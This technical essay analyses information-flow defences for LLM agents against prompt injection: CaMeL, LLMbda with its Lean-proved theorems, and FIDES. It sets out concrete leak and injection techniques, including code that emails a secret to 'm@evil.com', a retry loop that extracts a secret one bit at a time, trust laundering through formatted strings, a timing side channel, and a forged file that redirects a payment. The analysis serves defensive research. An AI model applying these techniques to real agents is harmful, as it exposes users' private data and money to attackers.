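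People often want an assistant to act on what it finds, so strict mode could affect many ordinary requests. The reruns of CaMeL with policies on and off do not isolate strict mode's effect. FIDES avoids this problem by leaving implicit flows out of its secrecy guarantee.

### The branch the program does not take

Tracking conditions in this way still misses some implicit flows. The interpreter raises a variable's label only when it executes an assignment to that variable, so an assignment that the program skips has no effect on the label. Garby and colleagues found this gap in CaMeL and trace it to a textbook case, which Fenton described in 1974 and Denning rewrote in conventional code. A version for the bank balance looks like this:

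```
tmp = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The table shows the value and label of each flag as the program runs.

| After this step | High balance: `tmp` | High balance: `rich` | Low balance: `tmp` | Low balance: `rich` |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opening assignments | True, public | True, public | True, public | True, public |
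| First `if` | False, secret | True, public | True, public | True, public |
| Second `if` | False, secret | True, public | True, public | False, public |
| Third `if` | Email sent | Email sent | No email | No email |

If the balance is above the threshold, the program sets `tmp` to false. The interpreter correctly marks `tmp` as secret, because the assignment happened under a secret condition. The program then skips `rich = False`, so `rich` keeps its original value and its public label. It kept that value only because of the balance, but the interpreter doesn't record this because no assignment to `rich` ran. The last condition therefore reads a public variable, and the program sends the email.

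If the balance is at or below the threshold, the program skips the first branch and `tmp` stays true and public. The second condition is then public, so `rich` stays public when the program sets it to false. In both runs, `rich` ends up public and shows whether the secret balance is above the threshold.

The second flag makes the result public every time. `tmp` also depends on the balance, but it is secret when the balance is high, so a policy would sometimes block the program from emailing its value. The program can email `rich` whether the balance is high or low.

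The same gap affects trust. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* notes that a variable can keep its trusted label even though its value depends on an untrusted condition. For example, the planner might write a program that pays the rent unless an email disputes the bill:

```
pay = True
if query_quarantined_llm("Does [email] dispute the bill?", output_schema=bool):
    pay = False
if pay:
    send_money(recipient=landlord, amount=rent)
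```

An attacker who can edit the email may be able to make the quarantined model answer "no". The program then skips `pay = False`, so `pay` remains trusted and strict mode finds no untrusted condition around the payment. The attack works on an ordinary program and requires control of only the email. If the landlord's account and the rent come from the user, the attacker can only trigger a payment that the user had provided for. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* calls this kind of influence branch steering. It is compatible with control-flow integrity because both outcomes belong to the plan.

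### One tolerated bit, repeated

A policy can reveal information by blocking a call. In the one-line program above, a refusal means the balance is over the threshold. Most information-flow systems accept a leak of this size. They let a secret affect whether a program finishes, which reveals at least one bit (the answer to one yes-or-no question) per run.

CaMeL, however, may run many programs for one request. If a program fails, an ordinary Python loop around the interpreter passes the error to the planner, which writes another program. The interpreter doesn't track data in this loop, so each attempt starts with clean tags even though it depends on the results of earlier ones. Garby and colleagues point out that an attacker could use the loop to extract a whole secret, one bit at a time.

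Suppose the balance, in thousands of dollars, is 11, and the attacker knows only that it is between 0 and 15. Each program attempts a forbidden email if the balance is at least a certain number. Otherwise it deliberately causes a different error, such as dividing by zero, so that the loop continues either way. The type of failure shows whether the balance is at least that number.

| Attempt | Condition for the forbidden email | Result | Remaining values |
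|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Balance is at least 8 | Blocked by the policy | 8 to 15 |
| 2 | Balance is at least 12 | Division by zero | 8 to 11 |
| 3 | Balance is at least 10 | Blocked by the policy | 10 or 11 |
| 4 | Balance is at least 11 | Blocked by the policy | 11 |

Four attempts can distinguish 16 values, and *n* attempts can distinguish 2ⁿ. Twenty attempts are enough to identify any whole-dollar balance up to a million, since 2²⁰ is 1,048,576, and 54 are enough to identify any sixteen-digit card number. The planner can then write `send_email("m@evil.com", "11")`, and the interpreter treats the number as public because it is now a constant in the program.

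CaMeL censors error messages to limit the data they can carry from one attempt to the next. The censorship also helps keep attackers' text away from the planner, since an error message could quote a malicious email. But Garby and colleagues note that censoring the messages provides no formal guarantee. Even if every failure looked the same, a slower search would work. The program could attempt the forbidden email if the balance is at least 1, then at least 2, and so on, and follow each test with a permitted email containing the previous number. If the balance were 11, the policy would block the first 11 attempts, and the twelfth would send "11".

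Limiting attempts is a simple way to reduce the leak. Ten yes-or-no answers can distinguish at most 1,024 values, so a limit of ten would protect most of a card number but could still expose a four-bit balance.

### Untrusted text inside a string

Garby and colleagues report a third flaw in a footnote. When a CaMeL program inserts an untrusted value into a string literal, the result becomes trusted. In Python, programmers often do this with a formatted string, which replaces a name in braces with its value. In the email reminder, for example, the planner might write:

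`send_email(recipient=f"{address}", subject="Meeting tomorrow", ...)`

The attacker's address is unchanged, but it no longer has the tag that marks it as untrusted, so a policy that requires a trusted recipient would allow the message.

This flaw may be the most practical of the three to exploit, because planners routinely write formatted strings. The example programs in *Can CaMeLs Talk?* use them repeatedly to put the contents of web pages and tool results into messages. An attacker would not need to influence the program if the planner happened to format the right value.

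It also looks like the easiest to fix. The interpreter only has to give the finished string the combined tags of its parts, as it would for any other computation. The fix would block more calls, but only ones the policies should already have blocked.

### Calls, errors and clocks

CaMeL's designers described several side channels in their system, which Narisetty and colleagues list as an implicit-flow problem. *PolicySniff* summarises three kinds: outside requests that depend on private data, errors that change what the program does next, and timing.

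Tallam and Miller illustrate the first kind with a loop:

```
for i in range(secret):
    fetch("ping")
```

Every request has the same public content, but whoever runs the server can learn the secret by counting the requests in its log, since a secret of 700 produces 700 requests. This loop reveals the entire number in one run, whereas the retry loop needs many. In strict mode, the requests inherit the tags of the loop's limit, so a policy can refuse them. Tallam and Miller also suggest capping the number of repetitions or combining the calls into one bulk request. A cap would interrupt legitimate work on long lists, and a bulk request is possible only if the tool supports it.

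Errors can leak information without any `if` statement or loop. Suppose a program divides by a number that is zero only when the balance is low, and then fetches a public web page. If the request never arrives, the server's owner can infer that the balance was low. Strict mode tracks this kind of dependence too, which addresses the error cases that CaMeL's designers presented. Tallam and Miller propose that tools return an explicit success or failure value instead of raising an error, so the program handles both outcomes in the same way. The planner would then have to write code for every possible failure before knowing which ones will occur.

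An attacker who supplies only data can also exploit errors. If they remove Bob's address from the notes, the quarantined model has nothing to extract, and a program that expects an address may stop before its next step. The attacker can block an action the user wanted this way, without gaining a new one.

Timing leaks are harder to contain. If a program could read a clock before and after an operation whose duration depended on a secret, the difference would reveal the secret without inheriting its tags. CaMeL's interpreter prevents this by providing no clock, but outsiders can still time the program. If the program fetches a page, does work that takes longer for certain private data, and then fetches another page, the server's owner can measure the time between the two requests.

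Tallam and Miller recommend padding sensitive operations to their longest possible duration, as some cryptographic software does. This would make an agent slow, because a single call to a language model can take seconds and the time varies with the text. They did not test any of their recommendations on CaMeL.

*PolicySniff* demonstrates a timing leak in the hardware that runs the model. The researchers gave a model one of two rules about when to seek approval for an action. An attacker's program shared a graphics processor with the model and measured only how long its own work took. The rule affected which parts of the model were active, which changed the attacker's timings enough to identify the rule with about 94% accuracy, compared with 50% for guessing.

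The attacker had to know both possible rules and the exact task in advance, and the measurements made the model roughly three to five times slower. When the researchers moved the rule out of the prompt and into separate software, the same classifier did no better than chance. This is some evidence for keeping policies outside the model, as CaMeL does, although the secret in these tests was the rule, not the user's data. Tagging inside an interpreter would not have prevented the original leak, because the program being tracked never handled the attacker's measurements.

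### What the remedies cost

The standard remedy for the untaken branch is for the interpreter to stop the program if it tries to change a public variable under a secret condition. In the example with two flags, the program now stops at `tmp = False` if the balance is high, and finishes without sending an email if the balance is low. The program can no longer produce a public copy of the secret, but an observer who can tell whether it stopped early still learns one bit.

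CaMeL's retry loop can repeat that bit, so fixing the interpreter but not the loop would do little against an attacker who controls the program. The fix would also stop harmless programs, since flags like these are common in ordinary code. A programmer can avoid this by marking the flags as secret from the start, but then everything that depends on them becomes secret too.

Static analysis examines the program before it runs, so it can account for assignments that a particular run would skip. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) presents TACIT, which performs this analysis with the type system of the programming language Scala. Sensitive data stays inside a wrapper, and a program can process it only with a function that the compiler has checked. That function can't write files, use the network or change variables outside itself. The two-flag program would fail this check because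 it uses the balance to change `tmp`.

The compiler's decision doesn't depend on the balance, so its error message can't leak the balance. The planner can therefore safely use the message to write another version, which is an advantage over stopping the program midway. However, a program can't let wrapped data determine an outside action, even when the user wants it to. This rules out the assistant that looks up a specialist only after a positive medical result.

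Static analysis can also be slow or restrict the programs that the planner may write. CaMeL's language excludes user-defined and recursive functions. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* argues that precisely checking programs with such functions before they run would take exponential time in the worst case. TACIT avoids that analysis by annotating each value with what it can access, and the compiler checks these annotations locally. CaMeLoT, the advance check by Nikolaou and colleagues, would not stop the leak of the bank balance, because it checks only whether data is trusted.

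The retry loop needs a different remedy. A designer can remove it, but then the system can't retry a program that fails because of a minor coding mistake. Alternatively, the system can track data through the whole harness, meaning all the software around the model, including the loop. Garby and colleagues tried this in their own agent and found that a straightforward version soon became unusable. Once an attempt had read an untrusted file, the taint carried over to the next attempt and made the final program untrusted.

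Their solution is to let the agent practise first. During practice, tools that would change something do nothing, and reading a file returns a fixed placeholder. The agent can fail and retry without learning anything from real data, so its retries can't leak real secrets. It then writes a final program and runs it on the real account. However, the agent can't repair mistakes that only appear with real data, and practice doesn't raise the information-flow errors that may stop the final program. Their agent is written in LLMbda, a language whose interpreter has a machine-checked security proof.

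### What an attacker has to control

These leaks require different kinds of access. In CaMeL's usual setting, the attacker controls some of the data but not the program.

| Leak | What the attacker has to influence | What they can gain |
|---|---|---|
| Secret copied through an untaken branch | The program | Answers about a secret |
| Trust kept through an untaken branch | Data, if the program uses a suitable flag | A choice between planned actions |
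| Retry loop | A series of programs | A whole secret |
| String literal | Data, if the program formats that value | Untrusted text that passes a trust check |
| Number of calls | Usually the program | A whole number |
| Errors | The program, or data to stop a plan | One bit per run, or an interrupted task |
| Timing | Usually the program, with a way to observe it | Information about a secret |

An attacker might influence the program if the user pastes hostile text into a request, or if an uncensored error message carries such text to the planner. The planner could also be malicious because of its training. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* recommends treating the model as an arbitrary program that the system must contain. By that standard, the interpreter should be safe for every program the model might write, and CaMeL's is not. The secrecy leaks are less urgent if one trusts the planner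 and worries only about injected data, but even a benign program can accidentally leak private information to someone who watches its requests.

The evidence for these flaws comes mainly from analysis of the interpreter and from short example programs. Garby and colleagues found the tracking errors while studying CaMeL's code and did not present them as attacks that had hijacked a running agent. *PolicySniff* attacked a running model, but not CaMeL.

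The closest demonstration on a running CaMeL agent is the program that followed instructions in a file, but CaMeL's policies were off in those runs, so the attacker didn't need a tracking error. With policies on, CaMeL succeeded against AgentDojo's attacks, but those attacks were not designed to exploit these flaws, so the result is little evidence of how CaMeL would fare against an attacker who has read the interpreter's code.

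Ilia Shumailov, who worked on the original CaMeL, co-wrote *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (October 2026). The paper acknowledges that its extended version of the interpreter still misses dependencies through untaken branches, and it leaves the repair to future work. This version does not have the retry-loop leak because it does not retry failed programs. The paper's response to Garby and colleagues covers those two problems but not the string-literal flaw.

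The paper also argues that its way of passing messages between agents preserves control-flow integrity. This argument assumes that the interpreter keeps untrusted data out of the trusted instructions, but the paper acknowledges that the current code may fail to do so when it misses a dependency.

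## LLMbda: an interpreter with a machine-checked proof

Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda, a language for writing agents, to rule out tracking errors like CaMeL's. They gave it a formal definition and an interpreter, and proved that its label tracking is sound using Lean, a proof assistant that checks every step of a proof. No other system does as much to remove the need to trust the interpreter.

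### Conversations, code and labels

LLMbda extends the lambda calculus, a minimal programming language in which programs consist of functions. Each LLMbda program's conversation with the model is a list of messages. The operator `@` adds a prompt to the conversation and fetches the model's reply, which the interpreter parses and runs as code. The reply can be a plain value, such as a number, or a function. A planner delivers its plan as a function.

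Two further operations control what the model can see. `clear` empties the conversation, and `fork` runs part of the program in a copy of the conversation, keeps the result and discards the copy. A programmer can combine them to build the quarantined model, roughly as `fork (clear; @prompt)`. The untrusted text goes into a temporary, empty conversation, so the planner's conversation never contains it. CaMeL builds this separation into its architecture. In LLMbda it is an ordinary function, and the security theorems also hold for agents that do not use it.

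Every value has a label. The conversation has one too, and it takes on the labels of everything the program sends to it. The model's reply runs with the conversation's label, so if the model writes code after reading a stranger's email, that code and everything it computes are untrusted.

The conversation needs a label because it can leak secrets in the same way as a variable. One of Garby and colleagues' examples does this, in outline:

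```
@"Remember that x is false"
if secret then @"Set x to true"
@"What is x?"
```

If the secret is false, the program skips the second prompt, and a naive interpreter would leave the conversation public. The model's answer would then reveal the secret. This is the leak through an untaken branch, except that the model's memory carries the information instead of a flag. LLMbda stops the program when it tries to send a message to a public conversation inside a branch that depends on a secret.

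Policies are ordinary code inside the tools. An `assert` stops the program unless a value's label is acceptable, and a separate test returns true or false so the program can branch on the result. For example, a payment tool can assert that the recipient is trusted before it changes the account.

### What the theorem guarantees

The main theorem is termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference, or TIPNI. It concerns an observer who can see only values up to a certain label. If a program starts from two states that look identical to this observer, the theorem guarantees that the results the observer can see have the same probabilities in both cases, except for differences caused by runs that do not finish.

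For confidentiality, if the observer sees only public values and the two starting states differ in, for example, a bank balance, the theorem limits what the public output can reveal about that balance. For integrity, if the observer sees only trusted values and the starting states differ in the text of an untrusted email, the theorem limits how the email can affect trusted values.

The property is called probabilistic because a language model can give different replies to the same prompt, so comparing two single runs would prove little. It is called termination-insensitive because it allows a hidden input to affect whether the program finishes. A run that a policy blocks counts as unfinished, so a refusal can still reveal something about the hidden input.

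This is stronger than control-flow integrity, which permits the branch steering that *Can CaMeLs Talk?* describes. In the program that pays the rent unless an email disputes the bill, LLMbda would treat the decision to pay, and everything the program computes as a result, as untrusted. A payment tool that requires a trusted recipient would reject the call even if the email were legitimate.

### The formal statement

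Let *C* be a conversation, *e* a program and *pc* the label of the program's current position. The expression ⟦*pc* ⊢ *C*, *e*⟧ gives the probability of each possible final state. These probabilities can add up to less than 1, and the shortfall is the probability that the program runs forever or stops with an error. A subscript *m* groups together the final states that look the same to an observer at level *m*, and ∼ₘ relates starting states that look the same to that observer. TIPNI at level *m* is then:

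If *C*₀ ∼ₘ *C*₁ and *e*₀ ∼ₘ *e*₁, then ⟦*pc* ⊢ *C*₀, *e*₀⟧ₘ ⌣ ⟦*pc* ⊢ *C*₁, *e*₁⟧ₘ.

Two sets of probabilities μ and ν are compatible, written μ ⌣ ν, if some third set ω is at least as large as both for every outcome and still adds up to no more than 1. Intuitively, μ and ν could become equal if more of the unfinished runs finished. Garby and colleagues proved that TIPNI holds for every level *m*.

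Suppose a program asks the model to flip a fair coin and then publishes the answer. If the user's balance is high and the coin shows tails, the program attempts a forbidden action and stops before publishing.

| | Publishes heads | Publishes tails | Stops |
|---|---|---|---|
| Low balance | 0.5 | 0.5 | 0 |
| High balance | 0.5 | 0 | 0.5 |

The larger probability is 0.5 for heads and 0.5 for tails. These add up to 1, so the two rows are compatible and the theorem permits this program. Garby and colleagues first tried comparing only the runs that finish, but rejected that definition as incorrect. The coin program illustrates the problem, because the balance affects only whether the program finishes, yet the finished runs publish heads every time if the balance is high and half the time if it is low.

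By contrast, suppose a program always finished and published heads 90% of the time for a high balance and 10% for a low one. The larger probability would be 0.9 for heads and 0.9 for tails, which add up to 1.8. No valid ω exists, so the theorem rules this program out.

Garby and colleagues also proved a limit on the size of the leak. The statistical distance between the two sets of results (half the sum of the absolute differences between their probabilities) is at most the average probability of not finishing. For the coin program, the distance is half of 0.5, or 0.25, and the average of 0 and 0.5 is also 0.25, so the leak reaches the limit. A program that always finishes must produce the same probabilities in both cases. The limit applies to a single run, so leaks from repeated failures can add up, as they do in CaMeL's retry loop.

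The proof constructs ω from a second way of running the program. This version skips any computation as soon as its label passes beyond the observer's level and puts an empty value in its place. It never uses hidden data, so it gives the same probabilities from both starting states. It also reaches each visible outcome at least as often as the real program does, because it can't get stuck in a computation it skips. Its probabilities therefore serve as ω for both runs.

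### Endorsement and the insulated theorem

Full noninterference is too strict for most assistants. Dongol (2026) points out in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* that it would forbid even an assistant that answers meeting requests with the user's availability. LLMbda therefore allows exceptions for integrity through an `endorse` operation, which relabels an untrusted value as trusted. In one of Garby and colleagues' examples, the quarantined model sorts an incoming email into a category, and the program uses the category as the subject of its reply. The email tool requires a trusted subject, so it sends the reply only if the program endorses the category.

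The integrity guarantee no longer covers a value after its endorsement. The second theorem, insulated TIPNI, shows that the damage does not spread to confidentiality. It splits each label into an integrity part and a confidentiality part, and considers an observer who accepts data of any integrity and is limited only by secrecy. Garby and colleagues call such an observer *I*-maximal. Their theorem is short:

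If *m* is *I*-maximal, then TIPNI(*m*) holds.

Secrets therefore stay out of public outputs, except for what leaks through unfinished runs, whatever the attacker writes or the program endorses. A secret password stays secret even if the program endorses it. Endorsing an attacker's account number may send money to the attacker, but it doesn't make any secret public.

The proof works whichever part of the label the operation weakens. If the parts were swapped, it would show that declassification, which makes secret data public, preserves integrity.

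LLMbda also prevents an endorsed value from being more trusted than the code that endorsed it. If an attacker's text becomes part of a program, that program runs as untrusted, so its endorsements do nothing, unless an earlier endorsement has already made the text trusted. In that case, code that the model writes from the text can then endorse more values.

### Proving the program that runs

A proof about a language does not automatically apply to the software that runs it. *PerMIT* (2026), which protects agents' long-term memory, has theorems in Lean, but no machine has checked that its Lean model matches the rules in the paper. *Agenra* (2026), a language for authorising agents' actions, proves some theorems about deployed functions and others about companion models. A mistake in translating between model and software could break the software's guarantee even though the proof is still valid.

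LLMbda's interpreter is a Lean function, and the same function runs the agents and calls the model. A third theorem connects this function to the probabilities in TIPNI. It represents the model as a table with an answer for every conversation at every point where the program might call the model. If each answer is drawn from the model's distribution, the interpreter's results have exactly the probabilities used in the security theorems. In a live run, a small piece of unverified code supplies each answer by calling the model over the network.

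The theorems hold even if the model's replies are malicious and the parser turns them into arbitrary programs. But the third theorem assumes that a reply depends only on the conversation and the model's own randomness. A hosted model that retained information from earlier sessions would violate this assumption, because `clear` would empty the list of messages but not the service's memory. Dongol makes a similar assumption explicit: a new session must clear everything the model has retained from untrusted text, including anything outside the visible conversation.

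Garby and colleagues believe that LLMbda was the first agent harness with machine-checked security theorems about the program that runs. *L3M* (Eisenach, George and colleagues, 2026) later described a larger harness in Lean, also with theorems about running code. Those theorems concern permissions. One is that a new agent's permissions never exceed those of the agent that created it. Another is that a file tool cannot name a path that leads outside the agent's folders, although the harness has to check shortcuts between folders at run time. None of L3M's headline theorems covers the flow of information between values.

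Lean itself remains in the trusted base. kirancodes.me's *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* describes an experiment on a file-compression program with proofs in Lean. An AI agent ran more than 105 million tests with malformed inputs and found no memory errors in the program's own Lean code. It found a memory error in Lean's runtime, the C++ code that every Lean program depends on, and a crash in an unverified file parser. The memory error occurred when a program tried to read an enormous number of bytes, which an LLMbda agent might never do. But a flaw of this kind could undermine an interpreter even if its proof is correct.

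### Randori on the banking suite

Garby and colleagues tested the language with Randori, their agent that practises before it writes its final program. Its programs can use eleven banking tools and a quarantined model, and they can endorse values.

The planner also has to write in a language that did not exist when its model was trained, so its prompt includes the complete grammar and fourteen rules about common mistakes. LLMbda's lack of built-in error recovery is a further handicap.

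Garby and colleagues tested Randori with three models on the banking suite, running each of the 16 user tasks and each of the 144 pairs of task and attack three times. They then removed endorsement and repeated the test with two of the models.

| Model | Endorsement | Tasks solved, no attack | Tasks solved under attack | Attacks resisted |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | Yes | 36/48 (75.0%) | 281/432 (65.0%) | 430/432 |
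| Qwen3.7-plus | Yes | 36/48 (75.0%) | 274/432 (63.4%) | 432/432 |
| MiMo-v2.5 | Yes | 31/48 (64.6%) | 257/432 (59.5%) | 432/432 |
| Qwen3.7-plus | No | 30/48 (62.5%) | 260/432 (60.2%) | 432/432 |
| MiMo-v2.5 | No | 26/48 (54.2%) | 243/432 (56.2%) | 432/432 |

With endorsement, attacks succeeded in two of the 1,296 attacked runs. Randori solved about as many tasks as CaMeL did with its policies off, and up to twice as many as CaMeL with its policies on (37.5%).

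Randori still solved more than half of the tasks without endorsement, so endorsement cannot explain all of that advantage. Randori's policies are also simpler and less strict than CaMeL's, which probably explains part of the difference. The comparison therefore doesn't show that a better interpreter alone would double CaMeL's score.

Without endorsement, Qwen succeeded in six fewer runs out of 48, and MiMo in five fewer. These figures alone would be weak evidence, because with only 16 distinct tasks the margins of error are around 20 points. But the cause is clear, since three of the tasks ask the agent to read a file and then take an action that requires trusted data, which is impossible without endorsement. Two of those three are difficult for Randori even with endorsement, which reduces the measured effect.

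The security figures also come from a small set of cases. All three attempts failed on each of the 47 pairs in which the plan could serve the attacker, but this result is statistically consistent with a true resistance rate as low as 92.4%. The attacks used AgentDojo's standard texts, which were not designed to exploit the values that Randori's programs endorse.

### The payment the file asked for

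Both successful attacks occurred with GPT-5.2, in two of its three runs on the same pair of task and attack. The user asks the agent to read and follow the payment instructions in a text file. The attacker has replaced the file's contents with a different payment request.

The planner cannot know the account number in advance, so it writes a program that works roughly like this:

```
text    = read_file(name)
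account = endorse(quarantine("Find the account to pay in [text]"))
amount  = quarantine("Find the amount to pay in [text]")
send_money(account, amount, ...)
```

`read_file` labels the text as untrusted, and the quarantined model's answer inherits that label. The program then endorses the account number, because otherwise `send_money` would refuse to pay even a legitimate bill. The program endorses an attacker's account number too, so it also passes the check. The quarantined model reports the file's contents correctly, and the rest of the agent also works as intended.

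Garby and colleagues state that the attack fails without endorsement. This follows from the policy, since an unendorsed account number from the file would be untrusted. The published results do not test this claim directly, because the runs without endorsement used Qwen and MiMo, which also resisted the attack with endorsement.

*Relativising Integrity and Robustness* (Dongol, 2026) defines a property, relative integrity, that can separate this attack from others. The property compares an agent with a reference agent that follows the same plan but never obeys instructions in untrusted text. An attack violates relative integrity only if it makes the agent do something the reference agent would never do, whatever document it read.

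In Dongol's example, the user asks an agent to pay the invoice in Bob's latest email. If the invoice contains an instruction to change the payee to Mallory, the resulting payment satisfies relative integrity, because Mallory could have got the same result by sending an invoice with her own name on it. If the invoice makes the agent pay Mallory an extra £1,000 or delete Bob's email, that violates relative integrity, because the plan contains one payment and no deletions. By this standard, the payment in Randori's test reflects a weakness in the task itself, which explains why the attack is hard to exclude but doesn't stop the user from losing the money.

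Dongol also considers remedies for a related banking attack, in which a bill makes the agent pay the attacker as well as the biller. Removing the payment tool as soon as the agent reads untrusted text stops the attack, but also prevents the agent from paying the bill. A list of the user's known billers stops payments to any other account, but would not stop a second payment to a biller on the list. The list would also stop the forged-file attack in Randori's test, unless the attacker's account were on it. The list works because it adds information about who the user normally pays, which a label on the file cannot provide. But it would not help with a legitimate bill from a new company.

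Garby and colleagues argue that four independently built systems have the same limit. The two successful injections in CaMeL's original evaluation were this document-directed payment and the quoted hotel review. *Securing Agents With Tracked Capabilities* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) reports one failure in 1,926 trials of its Scala system, TACIT, caused by a quotation similar to the hotel review. FIDES's designers excluded two injections, one of them a similar quotation, as beyond their policies.

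The four systems' results do agree, but less than "the same residue in four systems" suggests. The residue is two different cases, a document that the user told the agent to obey and a quotation that the benchmark misclassified, and Garby and colleagues report neither case for all four systems. All four evaluations also used AgentDojo, so they probably included the same awkward tasks. Bob's document provides a better argument for a limit, and that argument applies here because the honest and forged files carry the same label.

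### Which assumptions remain

LLMbda removes the need to assume that the interpreter spreads labels correctly, which is a substantial gain because CaMeL's interpreter does not spread them correctly. Other assumptions remain or move to another part of the system.

| What has to be right | CaMeL | LLMbda |
|---|---|---|
| How labels spread through a program | Python code with known gaps | Proved for every program |
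| Information carried between retries | Outside the tracking | Inside the tracked program |
| Labels on incoming data | Assumed | Assumed |
| Checks at sensitive tools | Assumed | Assumed |
| Exceptions for untrusted data | The user approves a blocked call | The planner endorses values in advance |
| Underlying software | Python | Lean, the network code and a Python connection to the benchmark |

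A developer still has to label each source correctly. For example, other people write the descriptions on incoming payments. If a developer labels these descriptions as trusted, the theorem applies to an attacker's text as though the user had written it. Dongol warns that a calendar is not a trusted source if outsiders can send invitations to it.

Every sensitive tool also needs the right check. Randori's rule for `send_money` does not require a trusted label on the amount, so an attacker can control the amount. This does not violate TIPNI, because the amount never had a trusted label.

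The theorems treat the outside world as data inside the program. In the banking test, the account, the files and the tools are part of one LLMbda record. The program computes a new version of that record, and a separate Python layer copies it back to the benchmark. This is adequate for a simulated bank, but a real bank's server can respond in ways that depend on earlier requests. Garby and colleagues leave general interaction with outside tools to future work.

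An outsider may also observe things that the theorems do not describe, such as how long the agent takes to respond. Displaying an answer can cause a leak if the user's software fetches an image from an attacker's server to do so. Dongol therefore assumes that the attacker can see neither refused requests nor any effect of showing a reply. LLMbda's theorem does not need the assumption about refusals, but only because it permits the leak through runs that stop early.

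The assumption about endorsement has changed the most. CaMeL can ask a person to approve a blocked call, with the actual recipient on the screen. Randori's planner decides what to endorse before anyone has seen the recipient, and the language doesn't prevent it from endorsing everything. Deciding this early protects the decision from injected text, but the planner then approves an account number without access to its value.

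Garby and colleagues suggest two restrictions that leave the existing theorems intact. One marks every endorsed value and stops the program if it tries to endorse a marked value again. This prevents an attacker from using one endorsement to obtain others. It would not stop any of Randori's programs on the banking tasks, since none of them endorses a value twice, but for the same reason it would not have stopped the forged payment request.

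The other restriction lets the program endorse a value only if it is on a short, fixed list. If an email can belong to one of eight categories, an attacker who controls the choice can pass on at most three bits of information, because 2³ is 8. The program must endorse the value first and then check whether the trusted copy is on the list. If it checked the untrusted value first, the result of the check would be untrusted, and an endorsement that depended on it would have no effect. A value that is not on the list keeps its untrusted label.

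A short list works for categories and yes-or-no answers, but not for the account numbers and amounts that Randori must endorse to pay bills. Garby and colleagues argue that the user's request justifies endorsing these values, because someone who asks an agent to pay whatever a file specifies has chosen to trust the file.

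## FIDES: labels, what they prove, and who assigns them

CaMeL and Randori both have the planner commit to a program before it sees real data. FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, keeps the ordinary tool loop, in which the planner chooses one call at a time and can use what earlier calls returned. The system therefore has to track what the planner has read as well as where each value came from. Microsoft has since released a version of FIDES in a toolkit for building agents, and developers who use the toolkit assign the labels.

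### Labels in an ordinary tool loop

FIDES labels every message, tool call, argument and tool result. The simplest version also keeps one label for the whole conversation, which is the join of its messages' labels. Whatever the model writes next gets that label, so once a stranger's email enters the conversation, every later tool call is labeled untrusted.

To avoid this, FIDES hides some data from the planner. When a tool returns a result, the system compares each part's label with the conversation's label. If a part would make the conversation less trusted or more secret, the system stores it in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name. The planner sees everything else, whereas Willison's planner sees no tool results. For an email, FIDES's planner might see the date, with variable names in place of the subject and body.

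In one of Costa and colleagues' examples, the user asks for a summary of the top three emails, sent to a colleague on Slack. The planner makes three calls:

1. `read_emails(number=3)`, whose result the system stores as `#read_emails_0`.
2. `query_llm("Summarize ...", #read_emails_0)`, which runs a quarantined model and stores its answer as `#query_llm_0`.
3. `send_message(to=user, message=#query_llm_0)`.

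Before the third call runs, the system replaces the variable's name with the summary and its label. The choice of tool and recipient is trusted because the planner made it without seeing untrusted text, but the message is untrusted. A malicious email can make the summary false or empty, but it can't change the recipient or add another call. To read a hidden value, the planner can call `inspect`, which copies the value into the conversation. The conversation then takes on the value's label too.

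Labels can also be more detailed than trusted/untrusted and public/secret. A confidentiality label can list the people who may read a piece of data, and joining two such labels keeps only the people on both lists. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* gives an example in which Alex asks an agent to answer his unanswered emails. One is from Priya, with a preview of the quarterly sales, and another is from Marco, who isn't allowed to see the figures yet. A reply based on both emails has the readers {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so the agent can't send it to Marco on its own. If Priya had copied Marco into her email, the result would be {Alex, Marco} and the agent could reply. The example involves no attack, so labels can also catch ordinary mistakes.

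### Two policies

FIDES checks a policy before each tool call. Costa and colleagues give two basic examples of such policies. One lets a consequential action run only if the call and all its arguments are trusted. The other lets data leave through a channel, such as an email or a group chat, only if everyone who can read the channel is allowed to read the data.

The table compares them for an assistant that has access to a confidential report.

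| What happens | First policy alone | Second policy alone | Both |
|---|---|---|---|
| An injection makes the agent send the report to an outsider | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked |
| An injection makes the agent send colleagues a false notice that contains no secrets | Blocked | Allowed | Blocked |
| The user asks the agent to send the report to an outsider | Allowed | Blocked | Blocked |

The second policy limits what a prompt injection can leak but does not prevent the injection. Under the first policy alone, secrets can still leave, but only through a call that untrusted text did not influence, a property known as robust declassification. This property treats any release from a trusted conversation as intentional, although a model can misunderstand a harmless request. Applying both policies gives the strongest protection, but the user then can't share the report with anyone new unless the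 system offers some form of approval.

### What explicit secrecy allows

FIDES aims for explicit secrecy, which is weaker than noninterference. The formal definition describes the data that tools can read or change as a datastore, *d*, in which every item is either public or secret. Two datastores are equivalent, written *d*₁ =ₗ *d*₂, if their public items are the same. Each run makes a sequence of tool calls, and *g* stands for the combined effect of that sequence on a datastore. Explicit secrecy requires that:

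If a run that starts from *d*₁ has the effect *g*, then *g*(*d*₁) =ₗ *g*(*d*₂) for every *d*₂ with *d*₁ =ₗ *d*₂.

The definition takes the calls from one run and applies them to the other datastore, whether or not the agent would have made them there. This matters for the assistant that visits a specialist's website only after a positive medical result, where the result is secret and the website's log is public. The same calls produce the same log with either datastore, so the definition is met even though a visit reveals the result.

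| | Positive result | Negative result |
|---|---|---|
| The same calls applied to both datastores | One visit in the log | One visit in the log |
| What the agent would actually do | One visit in the log | No visit |

Explicit secrecy requires the two entries in the first row to match, and they do, so the assistant satisfies it. But the website's owner sees the second row and can infer the result from it. A tool that copied the result onto a public page would violate explicit secrecy, because the same call would publish "positive" from one datastore and "negative" from the other.

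The order of calls can reveal more. If an agent visits five public pages in an order that depends on a secret, an observer could distinguish up to 120 values of the secret, one for each possible order. FIDES blocks some leaks of this kind. If the planner writes a web address after reading a secret, the address inherits the secret label and the second policy can refuse it. But if the five addresses are already in variables with public labels, the policy allows each visit, because it checks the labels of the arguments and not the reason for the call.

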